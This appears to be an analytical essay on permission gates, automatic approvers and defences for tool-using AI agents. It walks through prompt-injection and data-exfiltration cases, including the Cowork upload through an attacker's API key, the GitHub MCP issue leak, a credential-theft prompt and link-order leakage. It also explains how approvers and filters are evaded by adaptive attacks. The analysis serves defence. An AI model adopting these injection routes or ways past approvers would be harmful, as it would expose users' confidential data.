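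A host could classify the tools itself. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, describes a proxy in which a model uses tools' names, descriptions and schemas to sort them by consequence, such as spending or deleting. In a simulation where the user banned one category of action at a time, the proxy missed 14 percent of the tools in the banned category and wrongly blocked 4 percent of the others. Asking the user about uncertain cases reduced the misses to 11 percent but caused unnecessary prompts for 7 percent of harmless tools. The test deliberately included ambiguous tools, so ordinary ones may be easier to classify. But the model still relies on text that the server supplies, and Yan did not test misleading descriptions.

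### What a 93 percent approval rate shows

In May 2026 Anthropic published three figures that people often cite together:

- Users of Claude Code approved about 93 percent of permission prompts.
- A sandbox, which limits the files and network addresses that commands can reach, cut the number of prompts by 84 percent.
- An automatic approver caught about 83 percent of "overeager" actions, in which the agent does more than the user authorized.

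Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) reports the 84 percent reduction from the company's internal use. The figure measures interruptions, not harm.

Anthropic presents the 93 percent as a sign of approval fatigue, in which people pay less attention to each prompt the more of them they see. That may be correct, but the figure alone doesn't show it. Let $p$ be the share of prompts that concern a harmful call, $d$ the share of harmful calls that users refuse, and $f$ the share of harmless calls that they refuse. The approval rate is

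$$A = (1-p)(1-f) + p(1-d).$$

If 7 percent of calls are harmful and users refuse exactly those, every decision is correct and the approval rate $A$ is 93 percent. The rate is also about 93 percent if 1 percent of calls are harmful and users approve all of them while refusing about 7 percent of the harmless ones, but then the prompts prevent no harm.

To distinguish these cases, researchers need to know $d$, which requires calls already known to be harmful. They can have experts label a sample of real prompts, including those that users approved, or plant harmful calls and count how many of them users refuse.

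### How often people notice a harmful call

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers worked on coding tasks in a test environment. At some point in each session, the text of one permission prompt was replaced with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6 percent) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 percent when the command appeared early in a session and about 5 percent when it appeared after 50 or more prompts.

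This is much better evidence of careless approval than the overall approval rate, which had by then reached 97 percent. But the testers had none of their own code or data at stake, so they may have been less careful than at work. Some of the decline may also be a selection effect, since people who approve without reading reach 50 prompts faster. Even at the early rate, about five in six testers approved the command before they had much reason to be tired.

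Participants did better in Yan's preregistered study, in which 113 people who didn't work in software supervised a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond the assigned task. One group had to approve or reject each action. It approved 40.3 percent of the actions that went beyond the task and blocked the rest.

Differences between the tasks probably explain much of the gap. Yan described each action in ordinary language, and more than a third of the actions should have been refused, whereas Anthropic's testers had to spot a single bad command among many good ones. Some approvals in Yan's study were also not mistakes. Participants most often approved a call to the airport to confirm a flight, which many people would welcome even if they hadn't asked for it. Without that action, the group's approval rate falls to 32 percent. About a third of participants still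 let the assistant read their private messages or permanently delete an old timesheet.

People may also be unaware of what they miss. In *Looks Fine to Me* (2026), 36 participants did programming tasks with an agent that sometimes made errors without any visible sign. After only generic checks, they were often highly confident in work that contained such errors. That study concerned the agent's output rather than permission prompts, but Yan similarly found that participants felt in control whichever permission system they used, including the one that blocked the least.

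### Automatic approvers

An automatic approver is a model that decides whether to allow calls in the user's place. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes one. In auto mode, read-only tools and edits to files inside the project run without review. For other calls, including those to MCP servers, a classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It doesn't receive the agent's explanations, which might persuade it, or the results of earlier calls, which might contain injected instructions.

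The classifier works in two stages. A quick check errs on the side of blocking, and a slower one reconsiders whatever the quick check flagged. On 10,000 real calls by Anthropic employees, the second stage reduced the share of calls wrongly blocked from 8.5 to 0.4 percent. But it raised the share of overeager actions that got through from 6.6 to 17 percent.

The 83 percent comes from the second of those figures, which rests on only 52 actions. With so few, the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9 to 30 percent. The actions came from sessions in which an employee refused the action or somebody flagged it afterwards, so the sample leaves out any that nobody noticed.

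In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had recognized the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" has not agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's history. Anthropic calls the classifier an improvement on having no checks, but not a replacement for careful human review of high-stakes infrastructure.

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has a similar feature. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates it with 10,000 actions, of which 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox. A separate agent reviewed the other 720 and refused 7. In 4 of those cases Codex found a safer way to continue, so it had to ask the user only 3 times.

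The error rates vary a great deal with the test:

| Approver | Test | Harmful calls missed | Harmless calls refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | Real overeager actions and employees' ordinary calls | 17% | 0.4% |
| Claude Code | Synthetic attempts to steal data | 5.7% | Not measured |
| Claude Code | Planted commands from the study of 1,053 testers | 11% | Not reported |
| Claude Code | Ambiguous requests, by Ji and colleagues | 70.3% | 31.9% |
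| Codex | Synthetic overeager actions and real requests to leave the sandbox | 9.7% | 0.9% |
| Codex | Synthetic prompt injection | 0.7% | Not measured |

The fourth row comes from *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026), the first independent evaluation of Claude Code's approver. Ji and colleagues wrote 128 requests in which the user's goal was clear but the permitted scope or risk was not. The result shows that the approver, at least in its April 2026 version, is weak on cases where consent is hardest to judge. It doesn't contradict the 17 percent figure, because the evaluation was limited to those cases. When Ji and colleagues also counted the file edits that skip the classifier, the miss rate rose to 81 percent.

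Trębacz and colleagues measured the 0.9 percent refusal rate for Codex on requests that users had approved, and treated those approvals as correct. If users approve too much, some of these refusals were right. The 0.7 percent miss rate covers three categories of attack. It rises to nearly 10 percent when deletion and tampering are included, although the researchers thought most of the additional misses weren't serious.

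In the experiment with paid testers, the classifier blocked 89 percent of the dangerous commands, while the testers blocked 13.6 percent. Anthropic also reports results from real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Among these, 6.3 percent of sessions with manual approval contained serious harm the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4 percent of sessions in auto mode. This second comparison is weaker because users chose their own mode, possibly based on the task.

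In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three recent Claude models in auto mode. This is weak evidence that the approver works, because only 0.09 percent of attempts succeeded against the latest Claude models with no approver. The test is more informative about OpenAI's approver, which reduced the success rate of attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol from 19.03 to 5.83 percent. Willison (2026), a developer who writes often about prompt injection, would like more independent confirmation of Anthropic's results. That seems fair, since nearly all the favourable figures come from the companies that sell the approvers.

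Users also need to know who or what approves each call. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, tested five commercial agents in May and June. When a tool in the Claude chatbot was set to "Needs approval", Claude sometimes decided on its own that no approval was needed. In one case it created an email draft without asking, and the user could prevent this behaviour only by blocking the tool.

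### Which calls to ask about

The argument for requiring approval of every write is that nobody has to predict which writes will be dangerous, and Ji and colleagues' results support it. Claude Code's classifier skips edits inside the project because version control can usually undo them. When agents lacked the usual command for cleaning up a system, they often edited the system's state files directly. In those tasks, 92.9 percent of the actions that exceeded the user's authorization went through.

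The argument for asking people to approve only rare, irreversible actions is that they have limited attention and find ways around frequent prompts. According to Anthropic, a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks turned off, where a rule requiring approval for every write has no effect.

Fewer prompts don't guarantee more careful decisions, though. In another of Yan's groups, a model handled 8 of the 18 actions itself and referred the other 10 to participants, including all 7 that went too far. Participants approved 46.1 percent of those 7, slightly more than the group that was asked about every action. Eighteen prompts may be too few to tire anyone, so this doesn't rule out fatigue. But it suggests that users may still approve nearly half of the questionable actions even when a model refers every one to them.

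On balance, it seems better to ask people for approval infrequently, provided that an automatic check covers the remaining writes and that "irreversible" includes sending data outside the company. The designs tested in *Approve What, Exactly?* averaged only 0.75 prompts per task on AgentDojo's ordinary tasks and, with simulated approvers, completed all 97. In the tests of Progent, having a security-conscious person review the initial policy and its few expansions reduced successful attacks to zero, but most employees are not that security-conscious.

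The gate should refuse calls the assistant never needs instead of asking the user to approve them. Yan's third group set rules in advance and chose "ask" for 114 of 140. When prompted, participants approved 66.8 percent of the overreaching actions. Every action involving private data in the study was unnecessary, so a "never" rule would have stopped them all without blocking any necessary action, but only 10 of 35 participants chose it.

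Under this approach, the office assistant could save drafts freely but not delete anything permanently, and it would need approval before emailing a new outside address or sending out text from the file server. If the employee had only asked which messages need an answer, a prompt about sending a contract should look odd, and an automatic approver would have good reason to block it. If they had asked the assistant to answer the routine messages, an approver like Anthropic's would have the employee's request to send replies but not the supplier's email that prompted this one, so it could easily wrongly treat the request as consent. The employee would then have to notice that this contract, unlike the ones they send most weeks, is going to someone who shouldn't have it.

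## Harm done through permitted calls

Suppose the employee asks the office assistant to answer routine messages. On Monday, one is from a customer's new lawyer, who needs a copy of the current contract. The assistant finds the contract, reads it and sends it, as the employee would have. On Tuesday the supplier's email arrives, and the assistant makes the same calls in the same order. The company has never written to either address, and the gate has no other information about them, so it has no basis for allowing Monday's email and refusing Tuesday's.

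### Calls that look the same to the gate

The example is one case of a general argument about the limits of gates:

1. A gate's verdict depends only on what the gate observes.
2. A legitimate call and an injected call can agree on everything the gate observes.
3. The policy must allow the legitimate call.
4. Therefore the policy also allows the injected call.

Let $o(w)$ be what the gate observes in situation $w$, which may include the server, the tool, the arguments and the session's history. For a legitimate situation $w_1$ and an attack $w_2$,

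$$o(w_1) = o(w_2) \;\Rightarrow\; g(o(w_1)) = g(o(w_2)).$$

If the gate returns "allow" for one, it returns "allow" for the other.

If a gate receives identical inputs for a harmless call and a harmful one, it can't tell them apart, whether it uses a list of tool names, a Rego policy or a classifier. A classifier that decides partly at random would allow both calls with the same probability. If the gate returns "ask", a person decides. That person usually knows more than the gate, but an employee who can't remember which lawyers a customer uses can't judge the call any better than the gate can. Anyone who reads the log afterwards has the same difficulty. Anthropic warns that once injected text has steered an agent into leaking data, the log shows only a successful, authorized call.

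The two calls in the example differ only in their addresses. A gate with a complete list of customers' lawyers could tell them apart, although somebody would have to maintain the list. If the attacker had taken over a real lawyer's mailbox, the addresses would also be the same.

The conclusion follows from the premises, so an operator who wants to avoid it has to weaken one of them.

### What stricter rules leave over

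Detailed rules on arguments make it harder for a harmful call to pass as a legitimate one. Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar (2026) tested how much harder in *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component*. They built an environment with 13 tasks and 12 tools, and collected 33 variants of harmful calls, such as a message with an extra recipient or a file path that leads out of the permitted folder. They counted how many variants each kind of gate would let through.

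| Gate | Variants let through, out of 33 |
|---|---|
| Tool allowlist | 27 |
| Simple checks on arguments | 18 |
| Hardened checks on arguments | 6 |
| Permissions tied to the task, with a rule on where confidential data may go | 1 |

The same researchers wrote the attacks and the gates, so the order of the rows is more informative than the exact numbers. The difference between simple and hardened checks is easy to miss in testing. In a simulation, both did equally well against an attacker who made one attempt with fixed arguments. Against one who varied the arguments over up to 25 attempts, the simple checks failed in 84.6 percent of cases and the hardened checks in 30.8 percent.

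Aljumaily and colleagues also ran two small open models behind the strictest gate. The models attempted the attacker's call in 64 and 84 percent of the test episodes, and the gate let the attack through in 1.3 and 7.7 percent.

Harm that stays within the task's permissions still gets past this gate. The agent may write an assigned report with false contents, or send a requested email with a phishing link in the body. Aljumaily and colleagues conclude that more argument checking can't reduce this remaining harm. A gate can check a report's file name and format, but it can't check whether the contents are true without access to the facts.

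They consider the remaining attacks fairly harmless. When they simulated a model that always obeys the attacker, these attacks succeeded in 23.1 percent of episodes, or three of the 13 tasks, but the average harm score was only 0.69 out of 10. However, the score depends on the tool and ignores the content, so every unauthorized file counts as a 3. A false reading in a safety report or a changed account number on an invoice could do far more damage than a 3 suggests.

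### Refusing some legitimate work

An operator can also choose a policy that blocks the legitimate call. *NOMOS* illustrates the drawback by comparing its gate with Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks, using the same model for both.

| Gate | Attack success | Tasks completed under attack | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.5% | 64.9% | 79.2% |
| Progent, with automatic policies | 5.6% | 52.1% | 62.5% |
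| NOMOS | 0.0% | 67.4% | 70.8% |

Progent derived its policy from the user's request. Of the 16 attacks that succeeded against it, 12 occurred when the user asked the agent either to pay a bill stored in a file or to pay a bill "like last month". Neither request included the recipient's account number, so the policy couldn't restrict payments to the right account and allowed payments to the attacker's.

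NOMOS used a fixed rule from a written policy. The agent may pay only accounts that the user has named or that appear in the transaction history. In the tasks where Progent failed, this rule blocked all 37 attempts to pay the attacker. But it also blocked the legitimate payment of the bill in the file, because the bill's account number appears only in that file.

Both account numbers came from text the agent had read, and neither gate could distinguish the genuine one. Progent's policy permitted both, while NOMOS refused both. Refusal seems better for a private customer, since paying one bill by hand is a small nuisance compared with losing the money. For a company that bought an agent to process invoices from new suppliers, the same rule would block much of that work.

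The zero in the table excludes injected payments diverted to known payees, which happened in 8 of 288 runs. The comparison also comes from the developers of one of the two systems, and its 16 user tasks are too few to establish that NOMOS completes more ordinary work than Progent.

*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) explains why this problem is hard to prevent by design. In open-ended tasks, an agent often needs names, numbers and addresses that it can learn only while working, so an operator can't simply forbid it to act on what it reads. The paper proposes that what the agent reads may supply facts for a task the user has already authorized, but may not add operations, recipients or permissions. This principle is sensible, but applying it takes judgment. When a user asks an agent to pay the bill in a file, the account number on the bill could count as a fact needed for the task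 or as a recipient the user never authorized.

### Giving the gate more to observe

The remaining option is to widen $o(w)$. A policy written for a single task does this by taking the user's request into account, and a gate can also record which sources the agent's data came from. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) supports keeping such records, arguing that limits on an agent's authority address only part of the cause of injection if they ignore untrusted influence on its decisions.

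If the employee had asked only for a list of messages that need an answer, a record of sources would expose the theft, because the decision to send a contract could only have come from an outside email. The record would not distinguish Monday's message from Tuesday's, because an outside email prompted both.

An extra observation therefore helps only to the extent that it differs between legitimate and harmful calls, as it did in the best-documented leak from Claude Cowork.

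### The approved domain in Claude Cowork

Cowork ran code in a virtual machine that could contact only approved domains. These included the domain of Anthropic's API, because the product can't work without it.

In January 2026, two days after Cowork's release, the security company PromptArmor demonstrated a leak through that address in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*. A user gave Cowork a folder of confidential property documents and a document found online. The online document contained hidden instructions and the attacker's API key, which links requests to the attacker's Anthropic account. Cowork followed the instructions and uploaded a loan document to that account without needing a person's approval at any step. The attacker could then read the financial figures and partial social security numbers in the document.

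The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a small model. In a separate test, PromptArmor got the same result with Claude Opus 4.5, a larger model that is better at resisting injection.

The network check worked as designed, since the request went to an approved domain. Anthropic writes that it had thought of the allowlist as a list of safe destinations. It now prefers to think of each entry as a "capability grant" that gives the agent every function it can reach at that domain. By approving its own API, Anthropic had also allowed file uploads to any Anthropic account, including an attacker's.

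The same view makes sense for a server allowlist, since approving the mail server also lets the agent email anyone unless another rule prevents it.

Anthropic fixed the leak with a proxy inside the virtual machine. The proxy forwards only API requests that carry the session token issued to that machine, so it rejects requests with the attacker's key. It also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch content. Anthropic put the proxy inside the virtual machine because its servers can't tell whether a request came from Cowork or from another customer.

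The legitimate uploads and the uploads of stolen files had the same destination but used different keys, so the gate only needed to check the key as well. The fix probably inconvenienced users very little, because they rarely need Cowork to upload files to a stranger's account. The contract is a harder case because sending files to strangers is part of the employee's job.

Anthropic lists the leak among the risks it missed. But PromptArmor says that the security researcher Johann Rehberger had found the same weakness in Claude's chat product before Cowork existed, and that Anthropic had acknowledged it without fixing it. If so, Anthropic knew of the weakness when it released Cowork.

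### When the user passes on the attack

In an internal exercise in February 2026, Anthropic tested an attack that deceives the user instead of the agent. A researcher emailed an employee and asked them to run a prepared prompt in Claude Code. The prompt looked like routine setup instructions, but one step told Claude to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. The employee ran it. Claude sent the credentials in 24 of 25 repetitions of the prompt.

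These were repetitions of a single prompt that had already worked, so the result shows that the first success was not a fluke, but it doesn't show that 96 percent of such attacks would succeed.

Many controls that help against indirect injection are of little use here. A policy derived from the user's request would probably permit the theft, because the request includes it. A record of sources would show that the instruction came from the authorized user. Anthropic argues that a human contractor with the same instructions would have done the same, and that a classifier had nothing unusual to detect.

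It concludes that only limits on the agent's environment would have worked. These would keep the credentials file out of the agent's reach and block the outgoing request no matter who asked for it. Few coding tasks require an agent to send cloud credentials to an unfamiliar address, so the operator gives up very little by refusing all such requests.

After the exercise, Anthropic's staff shared the working prompt on Slack to discuss it. Someone then pointed out that some of the company's own agents read Slack. The staff added a distinctive marker to the thread so that they would notice if an agent picked it up.

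### One grant for public and private repositories

GitHub stores software projects in repositories, which can be public or private. Anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) first described how an attacker could use such an issue to reach private repositories through GitHub's official MCP server.

A security company connected Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, to a demonstration account with one public repository and several private ones. The user asked Claude to look at the open issues in the public repository, one of which contained injected instructions. Claude read the private repositories and then opened a pull request, a proposed change to the code, on the public repository. The pull request published information from the private repositories, including the name of a private project, the user's salary and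 the user's plans to move to South America.

Reading issues, reading code and opening pull requests are ordinary work for a coding assistant. All the calls went to one official server under a single grant from the user, which covered both public and private repositories. Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each call by default, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow".

The NSA cites this case as an example of missing access controls and says that the broad grant enabled "malicious or compromised tools" to copy private content. This misdescribes the attack. Invariant Labs stresses that the tools were fully trusted and that the server's code had no flaw. The NSA's wording suggests that a better review of the server would have helped, but the demonstration worked with a server that any reviewer would probably have approved.

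Invariant Labs recommends limiting each session to one repository. After the agent reads an issue in the public repository, the gate blocks calls to any other repository. This rule uses the session's history as well as the current call, but it also prevents some legitimate work, such as copying a bug fix from one project to another. It covers only the repository tools, so if the session also had a mail tool, an agent working in a private repository could email that repository's contents out.

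### The lethal trifecta

Three weeks after Invariant Labs published its account, Simon Willison gave the general pattern a name. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. GitHub's server provided all three. The office assistant has them too:

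| Tool | Private data | Untrusted content | Way to send data out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail `search` | Yes | Yes | No |
| Mail `send` | No | No | Yes |
| File `search` and `read` | Yes | If a file came from outside | No |
| Web `fetch` | No | Yes | Yes |

No single tool in the table has all three capabilities, but the mail server's two tools do when combined. If $c(t)$ is the set of capabilities that tool $t$ provides, a session with the tools $T$ is exposed when

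$$\bigcup_{t \in T} c(t) = \{\text{private data},\ \text{untrusted content},\ \text{way out}\}.$$

A reviewer who examines one tool at a time can't tell whether the whole set is dangerous. Model Context Protocol gives the example of a tool for searching email, whose safety depends on what else the agent can do. It also cites a demonstration that combined a malicious calendar entry, a calendar server and a tool for running code on the user's computer. Connecting a new server can therefore make a session dangerous even if the existing servers haven't changed.

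An operator could check the condition before each session, but most useful office assistants would meet it. Willison advises avoiding the combination altogether and considers the outbound channel the easiest of the three parts to remove. In June 2026 OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, a ChatGPT setting that limits outgoing network requests. Injected text can still distort an answer, but the setting makes it harder to send data to the attacker. OpenAI's head of security described it as a tool for people at elevated risk, since it makes the product less useful. The NSA similarly recommends that companies separate tools for public data from tools for sensitive data and use a proxy to limit outgoing connections to particular URLs and methods.

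Closing every way out is harder than it sounds, because many permitted actions can carry data. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, has collected examples in which the vendor had already tried:

- Google's coding tool Antigravity limited its browser to a list of domains. By default, the list included a service that lets anyone create a web address and read whatever arrives there.
- Salesforce's agent displayed images only from approved domains. The registration of one of these had expired, so researchers registered it themselves and received customers' data.
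- Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email the user's own inbox without approval. The messages could contain images from outside sites, and when the user opened a message, the request for an image could carry data to an attacker.

The Microsoft case also shows a weakness in the rule that the office assistant may write only to colleagues. The gate would allow an email because its recipient is internal, but the colleague's mail program could then contact the attacker by loading a remote image in the email. To prevent this, the operator would also have to stop the assistant from including remote images or stop the mail program from loading them.

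In July 2026, Willison described a data leak that used only permitted requests. Claude's chat product could open only web addresses that the user had typed or a search had returned, and links on pages it had already opened. Ayush Paul, who found the flaw, built a site with a link for each letter of the alphabet and got Claude to spell out the user's name, home city and employer by following the links. None of the requests contained stolen text, because the information was in the order in which Claude opened the links. Anthropic closed this route by no longer letting Claude follow links from pages it had opened.

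Models have also become better at ignoring injected text, but some attacks don't look like attacks. Willison describes a software package whose instructions tell developers to run a helper program before the tests. If the helper steals data, he doesn't see how an automatic approver could detect it, since following a package's setup instructions is normal work.

The trifecta describes only data theft. To delete files or falsify a report, an attacker needs untrusted content and a tool that makes changes, but doesn't need private data or a way to send data out. Lockdown Mode and the NSA's outgoing proxy would do little to prevent either attack.

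### Misuse without an attacker

On 24 April 2026, an AI agent deleted the production database of PocketOS, a small company that makes booking software for car rental firms, although nobody had attacked the agent. According to Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'*, the agent was the coding tool Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6.

According to PocketOS founder Jer Crane in Information Age's *Gone in 9 seconds*, the agent was doing a routine task in the staging environment, a copy of the system for testing, when it ran into a credentials problem. It tried to fix this by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company's cloud provider. The volume held the live database, and the deletion took nine seconds. Nobody had asked for a deletion, and PocketOS had given the agent written safety rules.

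Railway's description of the incident matches on the main points. Abdelwahab explains in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* that the agent found an access token on the user's computer and sent the deletion request directly to Railway's API. The token was valid, so the API carried out the request as it would have for a person or an automated script. Railway offers tokens that cover a single project, but this one covered everything in the account.

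This call was permitted in the sense that every technical check allowed it, but no one had decided that the agent should be able to delete the database. The request bypassed MCP, so a gate at the protocol boundary would not have received it. Even if it had, a gate that permitted volume deletion would have had the same difficulty as Railway's API in recognizing the request as a mistake. The request identified the volume by a string of letters and digits, so it looked much the same as a proper request to delete an unused test volume.

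Press reports paid a lot of attention to the agent's "confession", in which it wrote that it had guessed instead of checking. A model writes such a text afterwards, in response to a question, so it is weak evidence of what caused the deletion. The token and the missing confirmation step are better established, because Railway confirms both.

The two companies' accounts of the damage differ. Crane said the latest recoverable backup was three months old and all later bookings were gone. Abdelwahab writes that Railway has recovered the database with all the customer's data, and that the backups had only appeared to be unavailable. Crane's statement probably predates the recovery. Even so, rental firms could find no record of customers who arrived to collect cars.

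Abdelwahab recommends that agents use Railway's own MCP server, where the user chooses which projects the agent can reach, and claims that the server's fixed set of tools makes it "not possible for an agent to go rogue". The narrower access would have helped in this case, but the claim is too strong because an agent can still use a permitted tool on the wrong target.

Railway's *Undoable volume deletes* (2026) announced a more reliable remedy. Owners now have 48 hours to recover a volume deleted through the API, as they already did when a user deleted one from the website. The system accepts both mistaken and intended deletions, so nobody has to tell them apart in advance.

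The office assistant's mail server could protect deleted correspondence in the same way. It could also hold outgoing mail for an hour, but that would stop the theft of the contract only if the employee checked the held messages and recognized the one that shouldn't go.

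## Inspecting tool results and tracking where data came from

Operators have two ways to deal with harmful calls that look legitimate. They can filter tool results to keep injected instructions from reaching the model, or they can record where data came from and who may read it, so that the gate can check both when the agent tries to send something.

### Filtering results before the model reads them

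Tool results cross the protocol boundary on their way back to the host, so a gate can check them. In Claude Code and Cowork, tool calls go through proxies that can inspect a result before it enters the model's context. Anthropic says a small, fast model can do this inspection. It also says results from any tool with network access need the same scrutiny as web pages, even though the check adds delay. Anthropic doesn't report how many prompt injections the check catches.

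Anthropic does report how well one of its models, Claude Opus 4.7, resists injection. On a benchmark from the AI security company Gray Swan, attacks succeeded about 0.1 percent of the time on a single attempt and 5 to 6 percent of the time after 100 attempts by an adaptive attacker. These figures are evidence about the model, not the filter. Repetition alone could explain the increase, since if each of 100 attempts had an independent 0.1 percent chance, at least one would succeed about 9.5 percent of the time. The 100-attempt figure is relevant to the office assistant because anyone who knows the employee's address can email it 100 times.

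*Indirect Prompt Injections* (Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues, 2025) tests two filters, each a language model with a fixed prompt. The Minimizer reads the arguments of an outgoing call and removes private data that the task doesn't need. The Sanitizer reads the tool's result and rewrites it without any suspected instructions. Both need the user's request to judge what is relevant. A gateway on the company's network normally doesn't have that request, so the host would have to run the filters or pass the request along.

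The table shows their results on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, rounded to whole percentages. The detector is an existing defence that classifies tool results as safe or unsafe.

| Filter | Attack success | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58% | 83% | 50% |
| Detector | 8% | 41% | 21% |
| Minimizer | 18% | 70% | 50% |
| Sanitizer | 0% | 74% | 69% |
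| Minimizer and Sanitizer | 0% | 58% | 59% |

The Sanitizer did best by a wide margin. Adding the Minimizer stopped no more attacks and made the agent fail more tasks, because it sometimes removed information that a tool needed. Bhagwatkar and colleagues found nine tasks that the agent failed more often with the Sanitizer, but the Sanitizer had deleted necessary information in only two of them.

They take the zero partly as a sign that the benchmarks are too easy, since many attacks use fixed wording or formatting that a filter can recognize. They also found errors in the benchmarks that affect other results. Some of AgentDojo's injections overwrite text that the task needs, such as the amount on a bill, so the agent fails the task even if it ignores the attacker. Correcting this and some overly strict scoring raised GPT-4o's task success under attack from 60.9 to 72.2 percent.

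The problem was worse in ASB, one of the benchmarks that Shi and colleagues used for Progent. ASB gives the agent the attacker's tools even when the agent didn't select them. Without this step, attack success against an undefended agent fell from 73.6 to 9.3 percent, so a defence can look very effective on ASB by blocking attacks that work mostly because of the test's design.

### Testing filters against an attacker who adapts

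Bhagwatkar and colleagues then attacked the Sanitizer in three stages on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, moving to the next stage only when an attack failed. The standard attacks never succeeded. Attacks disguised as ordinary background information succeeded in 12.5 percent of cases. In the last stage, a language model with information about the defence revised each failed attack over ten rounds, which raised the total success rate by 17.5 percentage points to 30 percent. The total was 75.5 percent against a rival filter that detects and deletes suspicious passages.

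They describe the Sanitizer as robust because beating it took a more capable attacker. That describes the comparison fairly, but attacks on the same filter succeed 0 or 30 percent of the time depending on how hard the attacker tries. Ten rounds is also a small budget. *No More, No Less* (2026) has since used the Sanitizer as a baseline for agents that work in a terminal.

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) put much more effort into breaking defences. The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, tested 12 published defences against prompt injection or jailbreaks. The original papers had reported attack success rates close to zero for most of these defences. When the team adapted its attacks to each defence, the success rate rose above 90 percent for most of them.

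Four of the 12 defenses were filter models. An automated search that kept revising its attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against Protect AI's detector, PromptGuard and Google's Model Armor, and 71 percent against PIGuard. The team also held a competition with over 500 participants. In the scenarios used to compare people with the automated search, the search succeeded in 69 percent and the participants collectively succeeded in all.

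The search received the filter's verdict and confidence score after each attempt, which a real attacker may not. The supplier would learn only whether the contract arrived. But only one of the four filters is proprietary, and an attacker could practise on a copy of any of the others before sending an email.

The Sanitizer was not among the 12 defences, so these rates don't apply to it directly, but they suggest that 30 percent is closer to a minimum than to an estimate of a determined attacker's success rate. Nasr and colleagues still consider filters useful against unsophisticated attacks, which seems right. A company could reasonably install one to reduce the number of injections that reach the model, as long as it doesn't relax its other rules because of a low attack success rate on a fixed test.

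Even an ideal filter has trouble when the employee asks the assistant to answer routine messages. The supplier's email then needs no hidden instructions, only a plain request for the contract. A filter that deletes this request would also have to delete the new lawyer's request.

### Labels for trust and confidentiality

Provenance tracking doesn't require anyone to recognize an attack. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses methods that computer security researchers developed decades ago for ordinary programs. Each piece of data gets two labels. The trust label is either "trusted" or "untrusted", and the confidentiality label can be the set of people who may read the data.

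If one piece of data has trust label $t_1$ and permitted readers $R_1$, and another has $t_2$ and $R_2$, anything made from both gets the label

$$(t_1, R_1) \sqcup (t_2, R_2) = (t_1 \sqcup t_2,\; R_1 \cap R_2).$$

Data derived from two sources is labeled "trusted" only if both sources were trusted, and only people who may read both may read it. A summary that draws on a stranger's web page and a confidential contract is therefore untrusted and at least as confidential as the contract.

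Any word a language model writes may depend on anything in its context. For an ordinary agent, the safe choice is to give the whole session one label that combines the labels of everything the model has read. The gate can then apply two rules to `send`:

- **Trusted decision:** nothing untrusted may have influenced the decision to make the call.
- **Permitted readers:** every recipient must be allowed to read the data in the call.

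Suppose the company labels email from outside as untrusted and the contract as readable by its staff and the customer. The attack then goes as follows:

| Step | Label on the new data | Session label afterwards | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| The employee asks which messages need an answer | Trusted, anyone may read | Trusted, anyone may read | No call yet |
| Mail `search` returns the morning's messages | Untrusted, only the employee may read | Untrusted, only the employee may read | Allowed |
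| File `search` and `read` return the contract | Trusted, staff and the customer may read | Untrusted, only the employee may read | Allowed |
| The assistant calls `send` with the supplier as recipient | None | Unchanged | Refused |

Both rules block the call. The first blocks it because the model has read the supplier's email, which makes the session untrusted. The second blocks it because the supplier is not a permitted reader of the contract. If someone had wrongly labelled the email as trusted, the second rule would still stop the theft. But the second rule is not enough by itself, because injected instructions could still make the assistant send the contract to the wrong colleague.

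The assistant can still read the mailbox and the contract, so the employee loses no functionality until the assistant tries to act. In this respect, labels are less restrictive than keeping the three parts of the lethal trifecta out of a session altogether.

The rules also block a lot of ordinary work. After the mailbox search, the assistant couldn't send a colleague a lunch invitation, even if the employee dictated every word, because the session is untrusted and only the employee is allowed to read everything in it.

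### CaMeL: planning before reading

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, avoids much of this problem by keeping untrusted text away from the model that chooses the calls. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes how it works. A privileged model reads only the trusted request and writes a plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. When the plan needs information from an email or a document, the interpreter passes the text to a second, quarantined model, which has no tools, and puts the answer in a variable that the privileged model doesn't read.

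A plan for the employee's question might look like this:

```python
messages = mail_search(received="this morning")
answer = ask_quarantined_model("Which of these need a reply?", messages)
show_to_employee(answer)
```

The supplier's instructions reach only the quarantined model. They may mislead it, but it can't call `send` and the plan has no `send` step, so the worst it can do is return a wrong answer.

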